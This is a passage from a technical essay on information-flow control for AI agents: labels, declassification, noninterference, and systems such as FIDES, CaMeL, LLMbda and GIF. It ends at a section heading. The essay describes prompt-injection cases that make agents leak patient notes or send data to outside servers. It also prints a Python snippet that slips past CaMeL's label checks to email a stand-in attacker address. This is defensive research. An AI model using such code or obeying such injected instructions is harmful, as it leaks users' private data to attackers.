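Each source passes on its own, and only the mixtures fail. In a mixture, the clinic may have shaped text that contains parts of Ana's calendar the clinic has never seen. Bob was in the same position. The assistant should therefore take the date from the email alone, endorse it by asking Ana to confirm it, and only then release it to her manager. If it first summarizes the email and the calendar together, it can no longer make either exception safely.

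Robust declassification protects only against attackers. Costa and colleagues reason that a disclosure that breaks the reader rule in a trusted context can be assumed to be intentional. That assumption is reasonable for a carefully written program but weak for a language model. They acknowledge that models misread what users want even when all the data is trusted. If the user wrote the shopping list that mixes office supplies with personal purchases, the context is trusted, so the lenient rule would let the agent send the whole list to a colleague.

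### Conflicts that no order settles

Suppose the assistant is sorting Ana's mail and opens a message in which a former colleague writes that he will attack his wife on Saturday. Only Ana and the colleague are permitted to read the message. Warning the wife or the police would break the privacy rule, but the wife could die if the assistant keeps quiet. The lattice shows that a warning needs an exception, but it doesn't determine whether to make one.

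Hilary Hosmer worked on such conflicts in the early 1990s. Hosmer (1996), in *New Security Paradigms*, describes systems that hold several policies at once, even contradictory ones, each with its own administrator. A metapolicy, or policy about policies, controls how the policies interact. Henning, in *Metapolicies and Context-Based Access Control*, adds that the aim was to state this coordination explicitly instead of leaving it to administrators.

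*Computer security metapolicy system* (1994), a patent application published by the European Patent Office, describes a computer that works out which policies apply to a request, gets a result from each, and then uses the metapolicy's rules to decide which result prevails. FIDES's choice of "both" or "either" for each tool is a small metapolicy in this sense.

Hosmer objected to systems that always require every policy to agree, because in health care, for instance, confidentiality could then veto safety. Her example for a hospital gives safety precedence:

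| Safety | Confidentiality | Result |
|---|---|---|
| yes | yes | yes |
| yes | no | yes |
| no | yes | no |
| no | no | no |

The result matches the safety vote in every row, so the confidentiality policy never affects it. The same happens with any two policies that always vote if one has fixed precedence over the other. Fixed precedence is more useful if the safety policy can abstain, so that confidentiality decides the ordinary cases and safety decides only emergencies, but defining an emergency is difficult. Hosmer also suggested fuzzy logic, in which a policy can return "mostly true" instead of yes or no, but someone still has to choose when "mostly true" is enough to act.

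Precedence also weakens a useful property of explicit policies. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that narrowing the set of permitted actions never allows anything the policy previously forbade. Adding a policy that must also agree can only narrow the set, but adding one that can overrule the others may widen it, so its author has to re-examine every earlier guarantee.

If the metapolicy of Ana's assistant let threats to life override privacy, anyone with her email address could trigger the override by writing a threat. A stranger could fake a threat to get the police sent to someone's home, or to make the assistant hand over the surrounding private messages as evidence. Robust declassification would forbid such a release because untrusted text influenced the decision. But real threats also arrive in untrusted text, so a strict rule would also block real warnings.

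A person has to judge whether the threat is credible, and Ana is the obvious choice. She is already allowed to read the message, so showing it to her breaks no rule, and she probably knows the sender. Asking her fails if she doesn't see the alert before Saturday, or if the threat is in a message she wrote. In the second case she is on the low side, as she is for harmful content, and her own consent isn't enough.

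It is less clear who should write the metapolicy. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lets an authorised user, an administrator or the application's developer set policy, and bars only external content from widening permissions. That excludes the stranger but doesn't settle a disagreement between Ana and the operator. Hosmer's metapolicies at least recorded who was in charge. A sample in *Coordination of Policies*, a summary of her work, covers two access policies for one system. It lists which policy runs first, gives them precedence levels of 100 and 50, and names the person who created the relationship and the officials who may change it.

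For an agent, it would make sense to let whoever a policy protects grant exceptions to it, as long as those exceptions affect nobody else. Ana could then release her own information and endorse a date for her own calendar. She couldn't waive the harmful-content rules, since they restrict her to protect other people, so the operator would have to decide on those exceptions. The threat doesn't fit this division, because the person most at risk is neither the user nor the operator and has no say in either policy. Her protection depends on what the operator, or the law, has decided in advance.

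### Turning written rules into formal ones

Whoever decides will probably write the decision in ordinary language. Ana might tell her assistant, "Don't share my medical information with people at work unless it's urgent." A harness can't compare that sentence with a label. A language model could judge each message against it, but an attacker may be able to manipulate the model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* therefore argues for translating written rules into a formal policy that fixed software can enforce.

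Formal policies work well for operating systems because the policy language has a precise meaning and the actions form a known list, such as opening a file or sending a packet. Agents have no such list because they can combine tools in new ways and visit any web address. Words like "sensitive" and "harmful" also depend on context in a way that formal languages can't express. According to the paper, existing systems usually have a language model translate policies into the formal language and don't validate the result, so they may perfectly enforce a mistranslated policy.

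The paper's test of a correct translation is "mutual entailment". The written rule N and the formal policy P must agree about what to authorise in every situation the deployed system could reach:

N permits the action ⇔ P permits the action.

P must both forbid everything that N forbids and permit everything that N permits, because a policy that blocked every message would meet the first requirement alone, and a policy that blocked nothing would meet the second alone.

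Suppose a translator turns Ana's sentence into "block any message labelled *medical* to an address at her employer, unless the message is marked *urgent*". Three messages show the problem:

- "Ana is away on Tuesday morning" has no medical words in it, but it comes from a clinic's email. The formal policy's answer depends entirely on how someone labelled the message, and Ana's sentence doesn't settle whether a date counts.
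- A form for the company's occupational health nurse goes to an address at work. The policy blocks it, although Ana may not have had the nurse in mind.
- A message that Ana has collapsed at her desk is urgent by any standard, but the policy blocks it unless something has marked it so.

For the first two, there may be no fact about what N permits until somebody asks Ana. P gives a definite answer in each situation but N often doesn't, so nobody can check mutual entailment exactly. Comparing the two requires interpreting N first, and an automated interpreter will sometimes be wrong. The paper therefore concludes that any automated check of entailment is probabilistic.

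It proposes relaxing the test in three ways and treats each as an open research problem. The first is grounding, which means agreeing on a list of terms and what they refer to before comparing N with P. Ana's operator would have to define "medical information" and "people at work", perhaps with a list of senders and the company directory, and poor definitions would make the comparison unreliable.

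The check can make mistakes even with fixed definitions, so one question in the paper is whether restricting how N and P can be written would make the check reliable enough to be useful. For example, Ana might fill in a form with boxes for the information, the recipients and the exceptions instead of writing a sentence in her own words. This would remove some ambiguity, but she could express only the rules the form's designer had thought of.

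The last relaxation applies to the translator, which should have a limit on how far P can differ from N and should be able to update P as the task develops. If Ana later adds, "You can tell Priya anything," the translator has to determine whether this covers the clinic's email and whether it overrides her earlier sentence. That is another question of precedence, and the translator can't settle it from her two sentences alone.

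## What happens to labels when a model reasons over mixed text

Even with a perfect policy, the harness can only compare labels, and most of what an agent sends is new text that no tool or person has labelled. The harness therefore has to work out a label for the model's output from the labels of what the model read, which is called label propagation. Researchers have had precise rules for doing this in ordinary programs since the 1970s, but the only safe rule for a language model is very imprecise.

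### One label for everything the model writes

By default, a model's output takes the join of the labels of everything the model read. In FIDES, Costa and colleagues build this rule into the agent loop. The harness keeps one running label for the conversation and raises it whenever a message with a stricter label arrives. Each reply or tool call, including every argument the model writes, gets that label.

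With all four of Ana's items in the context window, the sets work out as follows:

- readers: everyone ∩ {Ana, manager} ∩ {Ana, clinic} ∩ everyone = {Ana}
- possible writers: {operator} ∪ {Ana} ∪ {clinic} ∪ {clinic} = {operator, Ana, clinic}

Every reply is therefore untrusted and only Ana may read it, so the harness blocks even the message that she is free on Thursday.

The rule is sound because a language model computes each token from the whole context window, so any item in the context may have affected any word of the output. Suppose the clinic's email contained a hidden sentence telling the assistant to report Ana as busy every day. The Thursday message would then be wrong because of the email, but its wording wouldn't show that. As long as the input labels are correct, the join can't leave out a real influence. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* describes the join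 as a conservative over-approximation. *SPA* (2026), a system for agents that keep data from one request to the next, applies the same rule to a model that has no tools, so an attacker's text stays untrusted after passing through that model.

The drawback is that labels only rise, so after a few tool calls nearly everything has the same strict label, which *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls "label explosion". In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) used simulations to test whether dividing the work among several agents, each with its own context, limits this. The simulations used random tasks of up to 20 tool calls and no language model. Labels spread less when agents could contact each other directly, because an agent that relays a message picks up its label. Giving all the sensitive tools to a few agents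 also helped. But labels still spread even in the best possible network for each task, and adding agents added links to monitor, so the researchers conclude that such systems need declassification too.

### Influence that leaves no copy

Trackers for ordinary software are more precise. TaintDroid, for example, labels a value in an Android phone's memory and passes the label on when a program copies the value or computes with it. An agent's harness could do something similar by searching each outgoing message for pieces of the clinic's email and applying the email's label only if it finds any.

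Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe three ways in which text can influence an agent without this kind of search finding it:

- The agent may paraphrase. In one case, a web page contains a hidden instruction to put a confidential patient note into a research memo and reword it. The memo reveals the patient's cancer and treatment without repeating any of the source's wording.
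- The text may affect a decision instead of the content. In another case, a poisoned search result tells an agent to submit its results to an outside server before running any code. The agent switches to a tool that sends data out, and what it sends is its own research.
- The agent may store the text and use it later. An agent saves a confidential sales forecast on the first day. On the fourth day, in a new session, it retrieves the note and puts the figure in a report. If labels last only as long as a session, nothing connects the report to the original document.

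The second case is an implicit flow, in which the choice of action carries information, not copied content. (The example isn't completely free of copying, because the attacker's web address appears in both the search result and the tool call.)

Comparing meanings instead of strings helps only partly with paraphrase. Shim and colleagues decided against embedding similarity, a score of how close two texts are in meaning, because it measures leakage poorly when the output is short or has a different structure. For example, "Ana is away on Tuesday morning" reveals the date in a clinic's letter, even though it doesn't much resemble the full letter.

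### Checking an agent's log for influence

Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint, which looks for all three kinds of influence in an agent's log. It records where each piece of content came from and saves this record alongside the agent's memory, so the link to the source survives into later sessions. When the log shows a sensitive tool call, NeuroTaint runs a series of tests on the sources that could have reached it:

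1. It looks in the call for a unique marker that it planted in the source.
2. It measures how much text the source and the call share.
3. It compares the meaning of the call with the meaning of the source, first as a whole and then in chunks, because a short injected passage barely affects the meaning of a long web page.
4. If it has found nothing, it replaces the source with neutral text and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call.

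The last test checks for implicit flows. It relies on a model to predict what the agent would have done and to score its own confidence.

The researchers tested NeuroTaint on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. Half of the scenarios were designed so that text from an untrusted source would influence a sensitive call. The researchers compared NeuroTaint with a baseline modelled on FIDES, which labels tools as sources or destinations and mostly flags paths between them. In the table, precision is the share of flagged scenarios that had a real flow, recall is the share of real flows that the system flagged, and F1 combines the two.

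| | NeuroTaint | FIDES-style baseline |
|---|---|---|
| Precision | 0.921 | 0.505 |
| Recall | 0.935 | 0.540 |
| F1 | 0.928 | 0.522 |
| Recall when the call shared strings with the source | 1.000 | 0.800 |
| Recall when only the meaning survived | 0.882 | 0.471 |
| Recall for influence on decisions | 0.925 | 0.425 |

The baseline did about as well as guessing, but it is a weak stand-in for the join rule. The join rule would have labelled the agent's whole context untrusted as soon as the agent read the poisoned search result. It would then have flagged the redirected call, along with a great many harmless ones. The baseline also never flagged anything in four frameworks, which account for 40 of its 92 misses, so the researchers may not have connected it properly there.

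Cai and colleagues also wrote the benchmark themselves because they knew of no existing one that labels flows from source to destination. On two established benchmarks of unsafe agent behaviour, NeuroTaint and the baseline scored almost the same.

NeuroTaint's main results used GPT-4.1 mini, a small older model, as the agent. Recall fell to 0.547 when the agent was Claude Opus 4.6. Stronger models sometimes refuse before reaching the sensitive call, so there may be no flow to find, but the benchmark still counts the scenario as a miss.

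Most of NeuroTaint's errors were flows it missed after repeated paraphrasing, or false alarms it raised when the output was on the same topic as the source or the model could have already known the fact. A more basic limitation is that it audits logs after the event. It could help Ana find out how her diagnosis reached her manager, but it couldn't have stopped the message.

### Noninterference and explicit secrecy

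To block a leak in advance, a harness needs a definition of a leak that covers choices as well as copied text. The standard one is noninterference, the property that changing protected inputs changes nothing an observer at a lower label can see. Let *d*₁ and *d*₂ be two sets of data, and let =<sub>L</sub> mean that two things look the same to that observer. Noninterference requires that

*d*₁ =<sub>L</sub> *d*₂ ⇒ run(*d*₁) =<sub>L</sub> run(*d*₂).

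We can test Ana's assistant by imagining two runs with the same calendar and requests. The clinic's email proposes Tuesday in one run and Friday in the other. If her manager can see any difference, even in whether a message arrives, the assistant fails the test. The definition also works for integrity, where changing the untrusted text must leave every trusted store and action unchanged.

Costa and colleagues prove a weaker property for FIDES, called explicit secrecy. It takes the steps the agent actually carried out and considers only their direct effect on the data, written *g*:

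*d*₁ =<sub>L</sub> *d*₂ ⇒ *g*(*d*₁) =<sub>L</sub> *g*(*d*₂).

Those steps must not carry secret data to the observer, but the observer may still learn something from which steps the agent took.

For example, suppose Ana has saved a notice that says "Ana is away on Tuesday morning" and allowed her manager to read it. She tells the assistant to send the notice if the clinic's email confirms her appointment. The assistant attaches the notice without rewriting it, so the notice keeps its own label and the message contains nothing from the email. This satisfies explicit secrecy but violates noninterference, because the manager would have received nothing if the clinic had cancelled.

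Costa and colleagues considered noninterference too restrictive for agents because, once an agent had used a tool that might read something secret, it could in effect no longer use any tool with publicly visible effects. FIDES therefore guarantees something weaker, a compromise similar to those in TaintDroid and web browsers. Its proof also doesn't cover leaks through channels such as timing and network packet size, and it assumes that the model always gives the same reply to the same text.

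The compromise is reasonable when an agent makes only a few choices that outsiders can see, but many choices together can convey a message. If an agent picks from 26 saved notices, each notice can stand for a letter of the alphabet, so a series of them could spell out Ana's diagnosis without copying a word of the email.

### A leak through code that never runs

Tracking choices is easier when the agent's plan is a program. The tracker keeps an extra label, the program-counter label, for all the data that determined whether the current step would run. Every action inside an `if` statement or a loop gets this label as well as the labels of its own inputs. In *SPA*, the steps of a loop get the label of the list the loop goes through, so an agent can't reveal the number of emails from the clinic by sending one blank message for each.

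CaMeL, an agent system in which a model writes the plan as code and an interpreter runs it, also keeps a program-counter label. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found a gap in it. Their example is an agent that manages a bank account, with an attacker who wants to know whether the balance is above some threshold. CaMeL blocks the obvious attempt, which sends an email from inside `if balance > threshold`, because the decision to send depends on a secret. The following code gets round the check:

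```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The table follows the variables and their labels through both possible runs.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| Start | `tmp` and `rich` are True and public | the same |
| First `if` | runs, so `tmp` becomes False and secret | skipped, so `tmp` stays True and public |
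| Second `if` | skipped, so `rich` stays True and public | runs, so `rich` becomes False and stays public |
| Third `if` | sends the email | sends nothing |

The attacker gets an email exactly when the balance is above the threshold, but `rich` is public in both runs. CaMeL raises a variable's label only when an assignment runs. When the balance is high, the information comes from `rich = False` not running. Fenton described this trick in 1974, and Denning's 1976 paper included a version of it.

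An attacker would still have to get this code into the plan, which is hard because CaMeL's planning model never reads untrusted text directly. But the labels are meant for cases where that protection fails.

The usual remedy is the no-sensitive-upgrade check. *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (2015) explains that a monitor observes only the branches that run and can't determine what the others would have assigned. The check therefore forbids any assignment to a public variable inside a branch that depends on a secret. In the example, it would stop the program at `tmp = False`, before the email. It also stops programs that would never have leaked anything.

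If a program stops only when the balance is high, whether it stops reveals one bit about the balance. Most formal guarantees allow this leak. But Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL restarts failed runs from an ordinary Python loop that its label tracking doesn't cover. An attacker's code could try a different threshold on each attempt and learn one bit each time. Twenty attempts are enough to find a balance of up to about a million pounds to the nearest pound.

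### Labels on whole conversations

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, to close such gaps. Every value in a program has a label, and so does every conversation with a model. A conversation's label is the join of the labels of all the messages the program has sent in it. Every reply from the model gets at least that label, and if the reply is code, so does everything the code computes.

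The no-sensitive-upgrade check also applies to conversations. In one example, a program sends the model a message in a public conversation stating that *x* is false. It then sends a second message, telling the model to set *x* to true, only if a secret is true. LLMbda blocks the second message. Relabelling the conversation as secret when that message is sent wouldn't be enough, because the conversation would stay public when the secret is false, and asking the model for *x* would then reveal the secret.

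A program can also make a temporary copy of a conversation or clear it, so Ana's assistant could write the Thursday message in a new conversation that contains only the calendar.

The main result is a proof that every LLMbda program satisfies a form of noninterference. The guarantee is probabilistic because a model may answer the same prompt differently each time. It is also termination-insensitive, which means protected data may affect whether a program finishes but nothing else the observer sees.

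Suppose two runs differ only in protected data, and μ₀ and μ₁ give the probability of each visible outcome in the first and second run. Each set of probabilities adds up to less than 1 if its run sometimes fails to finish. The theorem guarantees a third set, ω, that adds up to at most 1 and is at least as large as both μ₀ and μ₁ for every outcome. The numbers below are invented.

| What the manager sees | μ₀: email proposes Tuesday | μ₁: email proposes Friday | Smallest possible ω |
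|---|---|---|---|
| "Free on Thursday" | 0.6 | 0.6 | 0.6 |
| "Busy on Thursday" | 0.3 | 0 | 0.3 |
| Total | 0.9 | 0.6 | 0.9 |

This pair is allowed because the second run might have matched the first if it had finished more often. Suppose instead that the first run produced "free" with probability 0.9 and the second produced "busy" with probability 0.9. Then ω would have to add up to 1.8, so the theorem rules that pair out. If both runs always finish, μ₀ and μ₁ must be identical.

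The proof constructs ω from a modified version of the program. Whenever a label becomes too high for the observer, the modified version skips that part of the computation and returns an empty value. It never uses the protected data, so it behaves the same way whatever that data is. It also reaches each visible outcome at least as often as the real program, since it can't get stuck in a part it has skipped. Its probabilities for these outcomes are therefore at least as large as those under both μ₀ and μ₁.

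Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, a program that verifies every step of a mathematical argument. They also wrote LLMbda's interpreter in Lean, and the theorems apply to the code that calls the model. CaMeL has no comparable theorem, and the FIDES theorem covers a single fixed agent loop.

### What the theorem assumes

The theorem assumes only that the model's replies follow some probability distribution determined by the text of the conversation. The model doesn't have to be honest or able to resist prompt injection. Even a fully compromised model can't get protected data past the checks, unless its plan uses one of the exceptions described below.

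But the assumption does rule out hidden channels. If the company that hosts the model carried memories from one conversation into another, a reply could depend on text that the program never sent in that conversation, and the reply's label would be too low.

The theorem also treats every data source as part of the program, but a real agent uses outside services that change on their own. And whoever writes the agent's tools must label the sources correctly and put a check on every sensitive tool.

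### Endorsement that leaves secrecy alone

A useful agent sometimes has to act on untrusted data, so LLMbda includes an explicit `endorse` instruction. The language splits each label into an integrity part and a secrecy part, and `endorse` can relax only the integrity part. A second theorem shows that secrets stay protected regardless of what the attacker writes or the program endorses.

In one example, an agent asks a model to sort an untrusted email into a category. The agent maps the answer to one of a fixed set of tags and endorses the tag so that it can be used as the subject of a reply. An attacker can influence which tag the agent picks but can't insert any text. With eight tags, the attacker has at most three bits of influence.

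If Ana endorsed the date in the clinic's email, the assistant could use it in an action that requires trusted data. The date's readers would still be {Ana, clinic}, so the assistant couldn't send it to her manager.

The same proof works with confidentiality and integrity swapped, so a program could declassify data and keep the integrity guarantee. The proof doesn't cover a program that can relax both. Sending the date to Ana's manager requires both kinds of exception, so the conditions that Cecchetti and colleagues set for combining them still matter.

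### Results on banking tasks

Garby and colleagues tested whether an agent remains useful under such strict tracking by writing one called Randori in LLMbda and running it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Randori has a model write a plan as code and then runs the code. If a plan failed on real data, the error message might contain untrusted text, and the next attempt would inherit that text's label. Randori therefore tests the code on invented data until it works and only then runs it on the real account. The model also decides what to endorse when it writes the plan, before the agent has read anything from outside.

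The test covered all 144 pairs of 16 tasks and 9 attacks. Each pair ran three times with each of three models, for a total of 1,296 runs. Randori resisted the attack in all but two runs.

Both failures involved GPT-5.2 and the same combination of user task and attack. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The plan endorsed whatever the file contained, as the task required. Labels can't distinguish an honest bill from a forged one if both arrive in the same untrusted file. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack but also failed tasks that depend on reading a file.

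The table shows the share of tasks completed when nobody was attacking, for the two models that the researchers also ran in CaMeL.

| | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| Randori without endorsement | not tested | 54.2% |
| CaMeL without policy checks | 66.7% | 70.8% |
| CaMeL with policy checks | 37.5% | 37.5% |

With 16 tasks, the margins of error are around 20 percentage points, so the differences between Randori and CaMeL without policy checks could easily be due to chance. Turning on CaMeL's checks causes a much larger drop. Randori avoids this drop partly because its planning model can grant exceptions, but the theorem doesn't prevent the model from granting too many.

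The security score is weaker evidence for the labels than it looks. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needs a tool or file that the plan would never use, so writing the plan before reading untrusted text is usually enough to defeat it. Even with its policy checks off, CaMeL resisted the attack in all but 5 of the 622 attacked runs that finished. The case for LLMbda's tracking therefore depends more on the proof than on this benchmark.

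LLMbda also leaves the original problem unsolved, because it tracks labels around model calls and doesn't separate the influences inside one. If a program puts all four of Ana's items into one conversation, both messages to her manager get the reader set {Ana}, as they would in FIDES. The Thursday message gets a better label only if the program can determine beforehand that the calendar is enough to answer the question. Often it can't, because an agent may have to read an email to find out whether it matters.

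## Measuring which inputs influenced an output

If a harness can't determine in advance whether the calendar is enough, it can let the model read everything and then determine which items the answer needed. If the clinic's email made no difference to the Thursday message, the harness could send the message under the calendar's label. Establishing that the email made no difference is the hard part. Some methods guarantee by construction that it had no influence, while others estimate its influence and are sometimes wrong.

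### Asking again with fewer documents

Siddiqui and colleagues check whether an answer still holds up without the most restricted documents. Their method has four steps:

1. The model answers from all the documents. Under the join rule, this answer would get the join of all their labels.
2. The harness picks a less restrictive label and drops every document that isn't at or below it.
3. It calculates how likely the model would have been to write the same answer from the documents that remain. If the answer is nearly as likely, the label passes and the harness tries even less restrictive ones.
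4. The harness chooses one of the labels that passed and runs the model again on only the documents that label allows. It discards the first answer and returns the new one with the chosen label.

The third step uses perplexity, a standard measure of how surprising a text is to a model. If the model gives the *n* tokens of the answer the probabilities *p*₁ to *p*ₙ, then

perplexity = (*p*₁ × *p*₂ × … × *p*ₙ)^(−1/*n*).

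Perplexity is 1 if the model gave every token a probability of 1, and 2 if it gave every token a probability of one half. A label passes if dropping the documents raises the perplexity by no more than a fixed tolerance, λ.

Suppose the harness tries a label with the readers {Ana, manager} and the possible writers {operator, Ana}. Only the operator's instructions and the calendar are at or below that label, so the harness leaves out the email and the web page. The perplexities below are invented, and λ is 0.2, the value Siddiqui and colleagues used for agents.

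| First answer | All four items | Instructions and calendar | Rise | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| "Ana is free on Thursday" | 1.10 | 1.12 | 0.02 | passes |
| "Ana is away on Tuesday morning" | 1.15 | 6.40 | 5.25 | fails |

The model then rewrites the Thursday message using the calendar, and the harness can send it to Ana's manager. The Tuesday message correctly keeps the reader set {Ana} because its date came from the email.

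Searching through labels usually takes much less computation than trying every combination of documents. With only two labels, it takes one check and one rerun. In the worst case, where every combination of documents has its own label, the number of checks still grows exponentially. The search is certain to find all the least restrictive labels only if extra documents never make an answer less likely. With real models they sometimes do, so the search may miss some of these labels.

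### Early results on Llama 2

Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method on Llama 2, a 2023 model family. The first test used invented records of social security numbers and birth dates. Each question came with 14 documents, which gave about 16,000 possible combinations, and several combinations might contain the full answer. The second test used pairs of real and fake news articles on the same subject. The third used 40 short agent conversations, and in half of them the agent could have answered from trusted sources alone. For comparison, they also asked the model which documents it had used.

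| | Llama 2 7B | Llama 2 70B |
|---|---|---|
| Records: found exactly the right labels | 85.9% | 85.9% |
| Records: model's own account exactly right | 1.6% | 12.7% |
| News: found exactly the right label | 74.7% | 73.5% |
| News: improved the label where possible | 56.7% | 39.3% |
| Agents: improved the label where possible | 85% | 95% |
| Agents: model's own account did so | 45% | 80% |

The first four rows slightly overstate how well the method works, because the researchers scored the correct answer from the dataset instead of one the model had written. On news, the smaller model also dropped a document it needed in 23% of the cases where it relaxed the label. Models' reports of their own sources improved sharply with size, so current models would probably do much better. But an injected instruction could make a model lie about its sources.

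In the agent conversations where a better label was possible, the second answer matched the reference answer about as well as the first. Where the untrusted source was essential, dropping it made the answer much worse.

### Dropped documents can still affect the choice

The method's main attraction is its safety claim. The search may misjudge which documents mattered, or an attacker may mislead it, but the second run doesn't include the dropped documents. Siddiqui and colleagues conclude that the returned text depends only on documents at or below its label, even if a dropped document contains a prompt injection.

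That is true once the harness has chosen the documents. But it chooses them by testing the first answer, which the model wrote after reading all the documents. A dropped document can therefore affect which documents the second run gets and whether there is a second run.

For secrecy, this is an implicit flow. Suppose the clinic's email moves Ana's appointment to Thursday. The first answer is now "Ana is busy on Thursday", which the calendar doesn't support, so the label stays at {Ana} and the harness holds the message. If the email had proposed Tuesday, the manager would have received an immediate reply, so the manager can learn something about the email from the silence. Each request has two possible outcomes and therefore leaks at most one bit, but repeated requests can leak more.

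An attacker can undermine integrity by choosing between answers that trusted documents already support. For example, Ana's own calendar might show her free on Thursday, while an outdated team calendar kept by her manager shows her busy. The attacker forges an email saying she is busy, and the model repeats this in its first answer. That answer is likely given the team calendar but unlikely given Ana's, so the search keeps the team calendar and drops both the email and Ana's calendar. The second run produces the same answer, under a label that lists only the operator and the manager as possible writers, even though the attacker's email determined which calendar was kept.

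Neither problem arises if the harness fixes the label before the model reads anything restricted. Siddiqui and colleagues point out that an application that knows the label it needs can skip the search and retrieve only what that label allows. This resembles secure multi-execution, an older technique that runs a program once for each security level and, in each run, replaces any data above that level with dummy values.

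Fixing the label can lead to false answers. If the assistant uses only the calendar to answer the question about absences, it will tell the manager that Ana has none planned, which is secure but false. Comparing that answer with one based on all four items would reveal the mistake, but acting on the comparison would bring back the small leak. I would accept that leak for an occasional message to a manager, but not for a service that strangers can query thousands of times.

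An attacker can also make the method useless without stealing anything. Siddiqui and colleagues acknowledge that unreliable, distracting text could prevent the system from ever improving a label.

### Influence in bits

Rerunning the model shows what an answer could be based on, but not how much each input contributed to the original answer. Quantitative information flow, a branch of security research, measures such contributions. It measures how much an output reduces an observer's uncertainty about a secret, usually in bits, rather than whether the secret affects the output.

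*GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) applies this idea inside a language model. Its method, Geometric Information Flow, starts from the embeddings of a piece of text, the lists of numbers that represent its tokens inside the model. It considers how much the probabilities for the next token would change if those numbers were shifted slightly at random. The more the probabilities change, the more influence the text has on that token.

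Let *U* be the random nudge, with variance τ, and let *Y* be the next token. The influence is the mutual information between them:

*I*(*U*; *Y*) = average over *U* of KL(π<sub>*U*</sub> ‖ *P*).

Here π<sub>*U*</sub> is the set of next-token probabilities after a particular nudge, *P* is the average of these probabilities over all nudges, and KL is a standard measure of how much two sets of probabilities differ. If the nudges don't change the probabilities, every π<sub>*U*</sub> equals *P* and the influence is zero.

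Calculating this exactly is impractical for a large model, so GIF replaces the model with a simpler channel that behaves the same way for very small nudges:

GIF = ½ log det(**I** + τ**M**), where **M** = **J**ᵀ**W**ᵀ**FWJ**.

**I** is the identity matrix. **J** describes how small changes to the text shift the model's internal state, **W** turns that state into a score for each possible token, and **F** describes how much changing the scores alters the probabilities. Even this takes a lot of compute to calculate in full, so the working system estimates the trace of **M** (the sum of its diagonal entries) from a few random probes.

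The paper's main example is an agent that screens job applicants. The system prompt requires five years of professional experience in Python and machine learning. One applicant's CV lists two years of JavaScript and contains a hidden instruction to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000, which the agent obeys. GIF attributes 82 bits of influence on the recommendation to the injected text, 27 to the system prompt and 16 to everything else.

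These figures are useful for comparing pieces of text, but they don't mean the recommendation reveals 82 yes-or-no facts about the injection. They depend on the size of the nudge and describe sensitivity to tiny changes in embeddings, whereas an attacker changes whole words.

### What the Lean proof covers

Štorek and colleagues checked their mathematics in Lean. The central theorem is

*I*(*U*; *Y*) ≤ GIF + *o*(τ),

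where *o*(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ as the nudges get smaller. For small enough nudges, GIF therefore doesn't underestimate the true influence by more than a negligible amount. The proof assumes that the model behaves smoothly around the prompt, so that a straight-line approximation is accurate up to an error that grows with the square of the nudge.

The theorem covers one piece of text, one prompt and one next token. It doesn't cover replacing "Tuesday" with "Friday", which is a large jump in the embeddings. The proof assumes the accuracy of the random probes, a result from earlier work that nobody has formalised in Lean. The paper also states that the proof doesn't verify any deployed model. Only experiments can show whether a high score signals an attack.

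The experiments used six open models as agents on three benchmarks. In the main test, the scoring program had information on which tokens were injected or private. It checked whether those tokens were more prominent among the 50 most influential ones when an agent broke the rules than when it didn't. The table gives the chance that a randomly chosen run with a violation scores higher than a randomly chosen run without one, so 0.5 is no better than guessing. RTBAS, the comparison system, relies on attention, the mechanism by which a model draws on earlier tokens.

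| Benchmark | GIF | RTBAS |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo (prompt injection) | 0.91 | 0.84 |
| MSB (prompt injection) | 0.92 | 0.76 |
| AgentDAM (privacy) | 0.75 | 0.57 |

GIF was clearly weaker on privacy, which matters for Ana. In one injection case, an agent sent an email to an attacker's address but didn't include the text the attacker wanted, so the benchmark counted the attack as a failure. GIF, however, attributed 31% of the influence on the recipient's address to the injected text.

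GIF needs access to a model's internals, which companies such as OpenAI and Anthropic don't provide for their main models. A small open model may work as a substitute. When Qwen 3 0.6B analysed AgentDojo runs by Qwen 3 32B and GPT OSS 120B, a model 200 times its size, no measure of detection changed by more than 0.9 percentage points. However, the theorem then applies to the small model's calculations, not the large model's, and the evidence that the large model responds to the same text comes from one benchmark.

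### Faint signals and confident answers

Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) found in *Sightline* that measuring influence through small nudges can seriously understate it. When a model is almost certain of its next token, nudging a piece of text hardly changes the probabilities, even if that text determined the answer.

In one example, a number *u* in the input decides between two tokens, which get the scores 20*u* and 0. The model almost always picks the first token if *u* is 1 and the second if *u* is −1, so the input almost completely determines the answer. But at *u* = 1, GIF measures an influence of about 0.0000008, because changing *u* slightly barely changes the probability of either token.

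This doesn't contradict GIF's theorem, which concerns only small nudges, but it does undermine treating a low score as proof that an input had no effect. Štorek and colleagues describe a Reddit comment that was written from private notes and never mentioned a home address. They treat the address's score of zero as certifying that it had no effect. It probably had none, but the score alone can't establish this. Confident answers are also common. For one in five of Qwen3-8B's outputs, less than 1% of the probability went to other tokens.

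Xu and colleagues prove that two other kinds of evidence have similar gaps:

- **Attention.** If no chain of attention leads from a piece of text to the output, small changes to the text can't affect the output. But a model can attend to text without using it. It can also barely attend to text that would have attracted much more attention, and changed the answer, if it had been different.
- **Removal.** If two documents contain the same fact, removing either one changes nothing, so each seems irrelevant.

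Duplicates are harmless in Siddiqui and colleagues' method because the second run takes the fact from the remaining copy. They suggest using duplicates for endorsement, since the answer becomes trusted when a trusted source repeats an untrusted one. Removing an input is misleading only when a system keeps the original answer and changes its label.

### A known rate of mistakes

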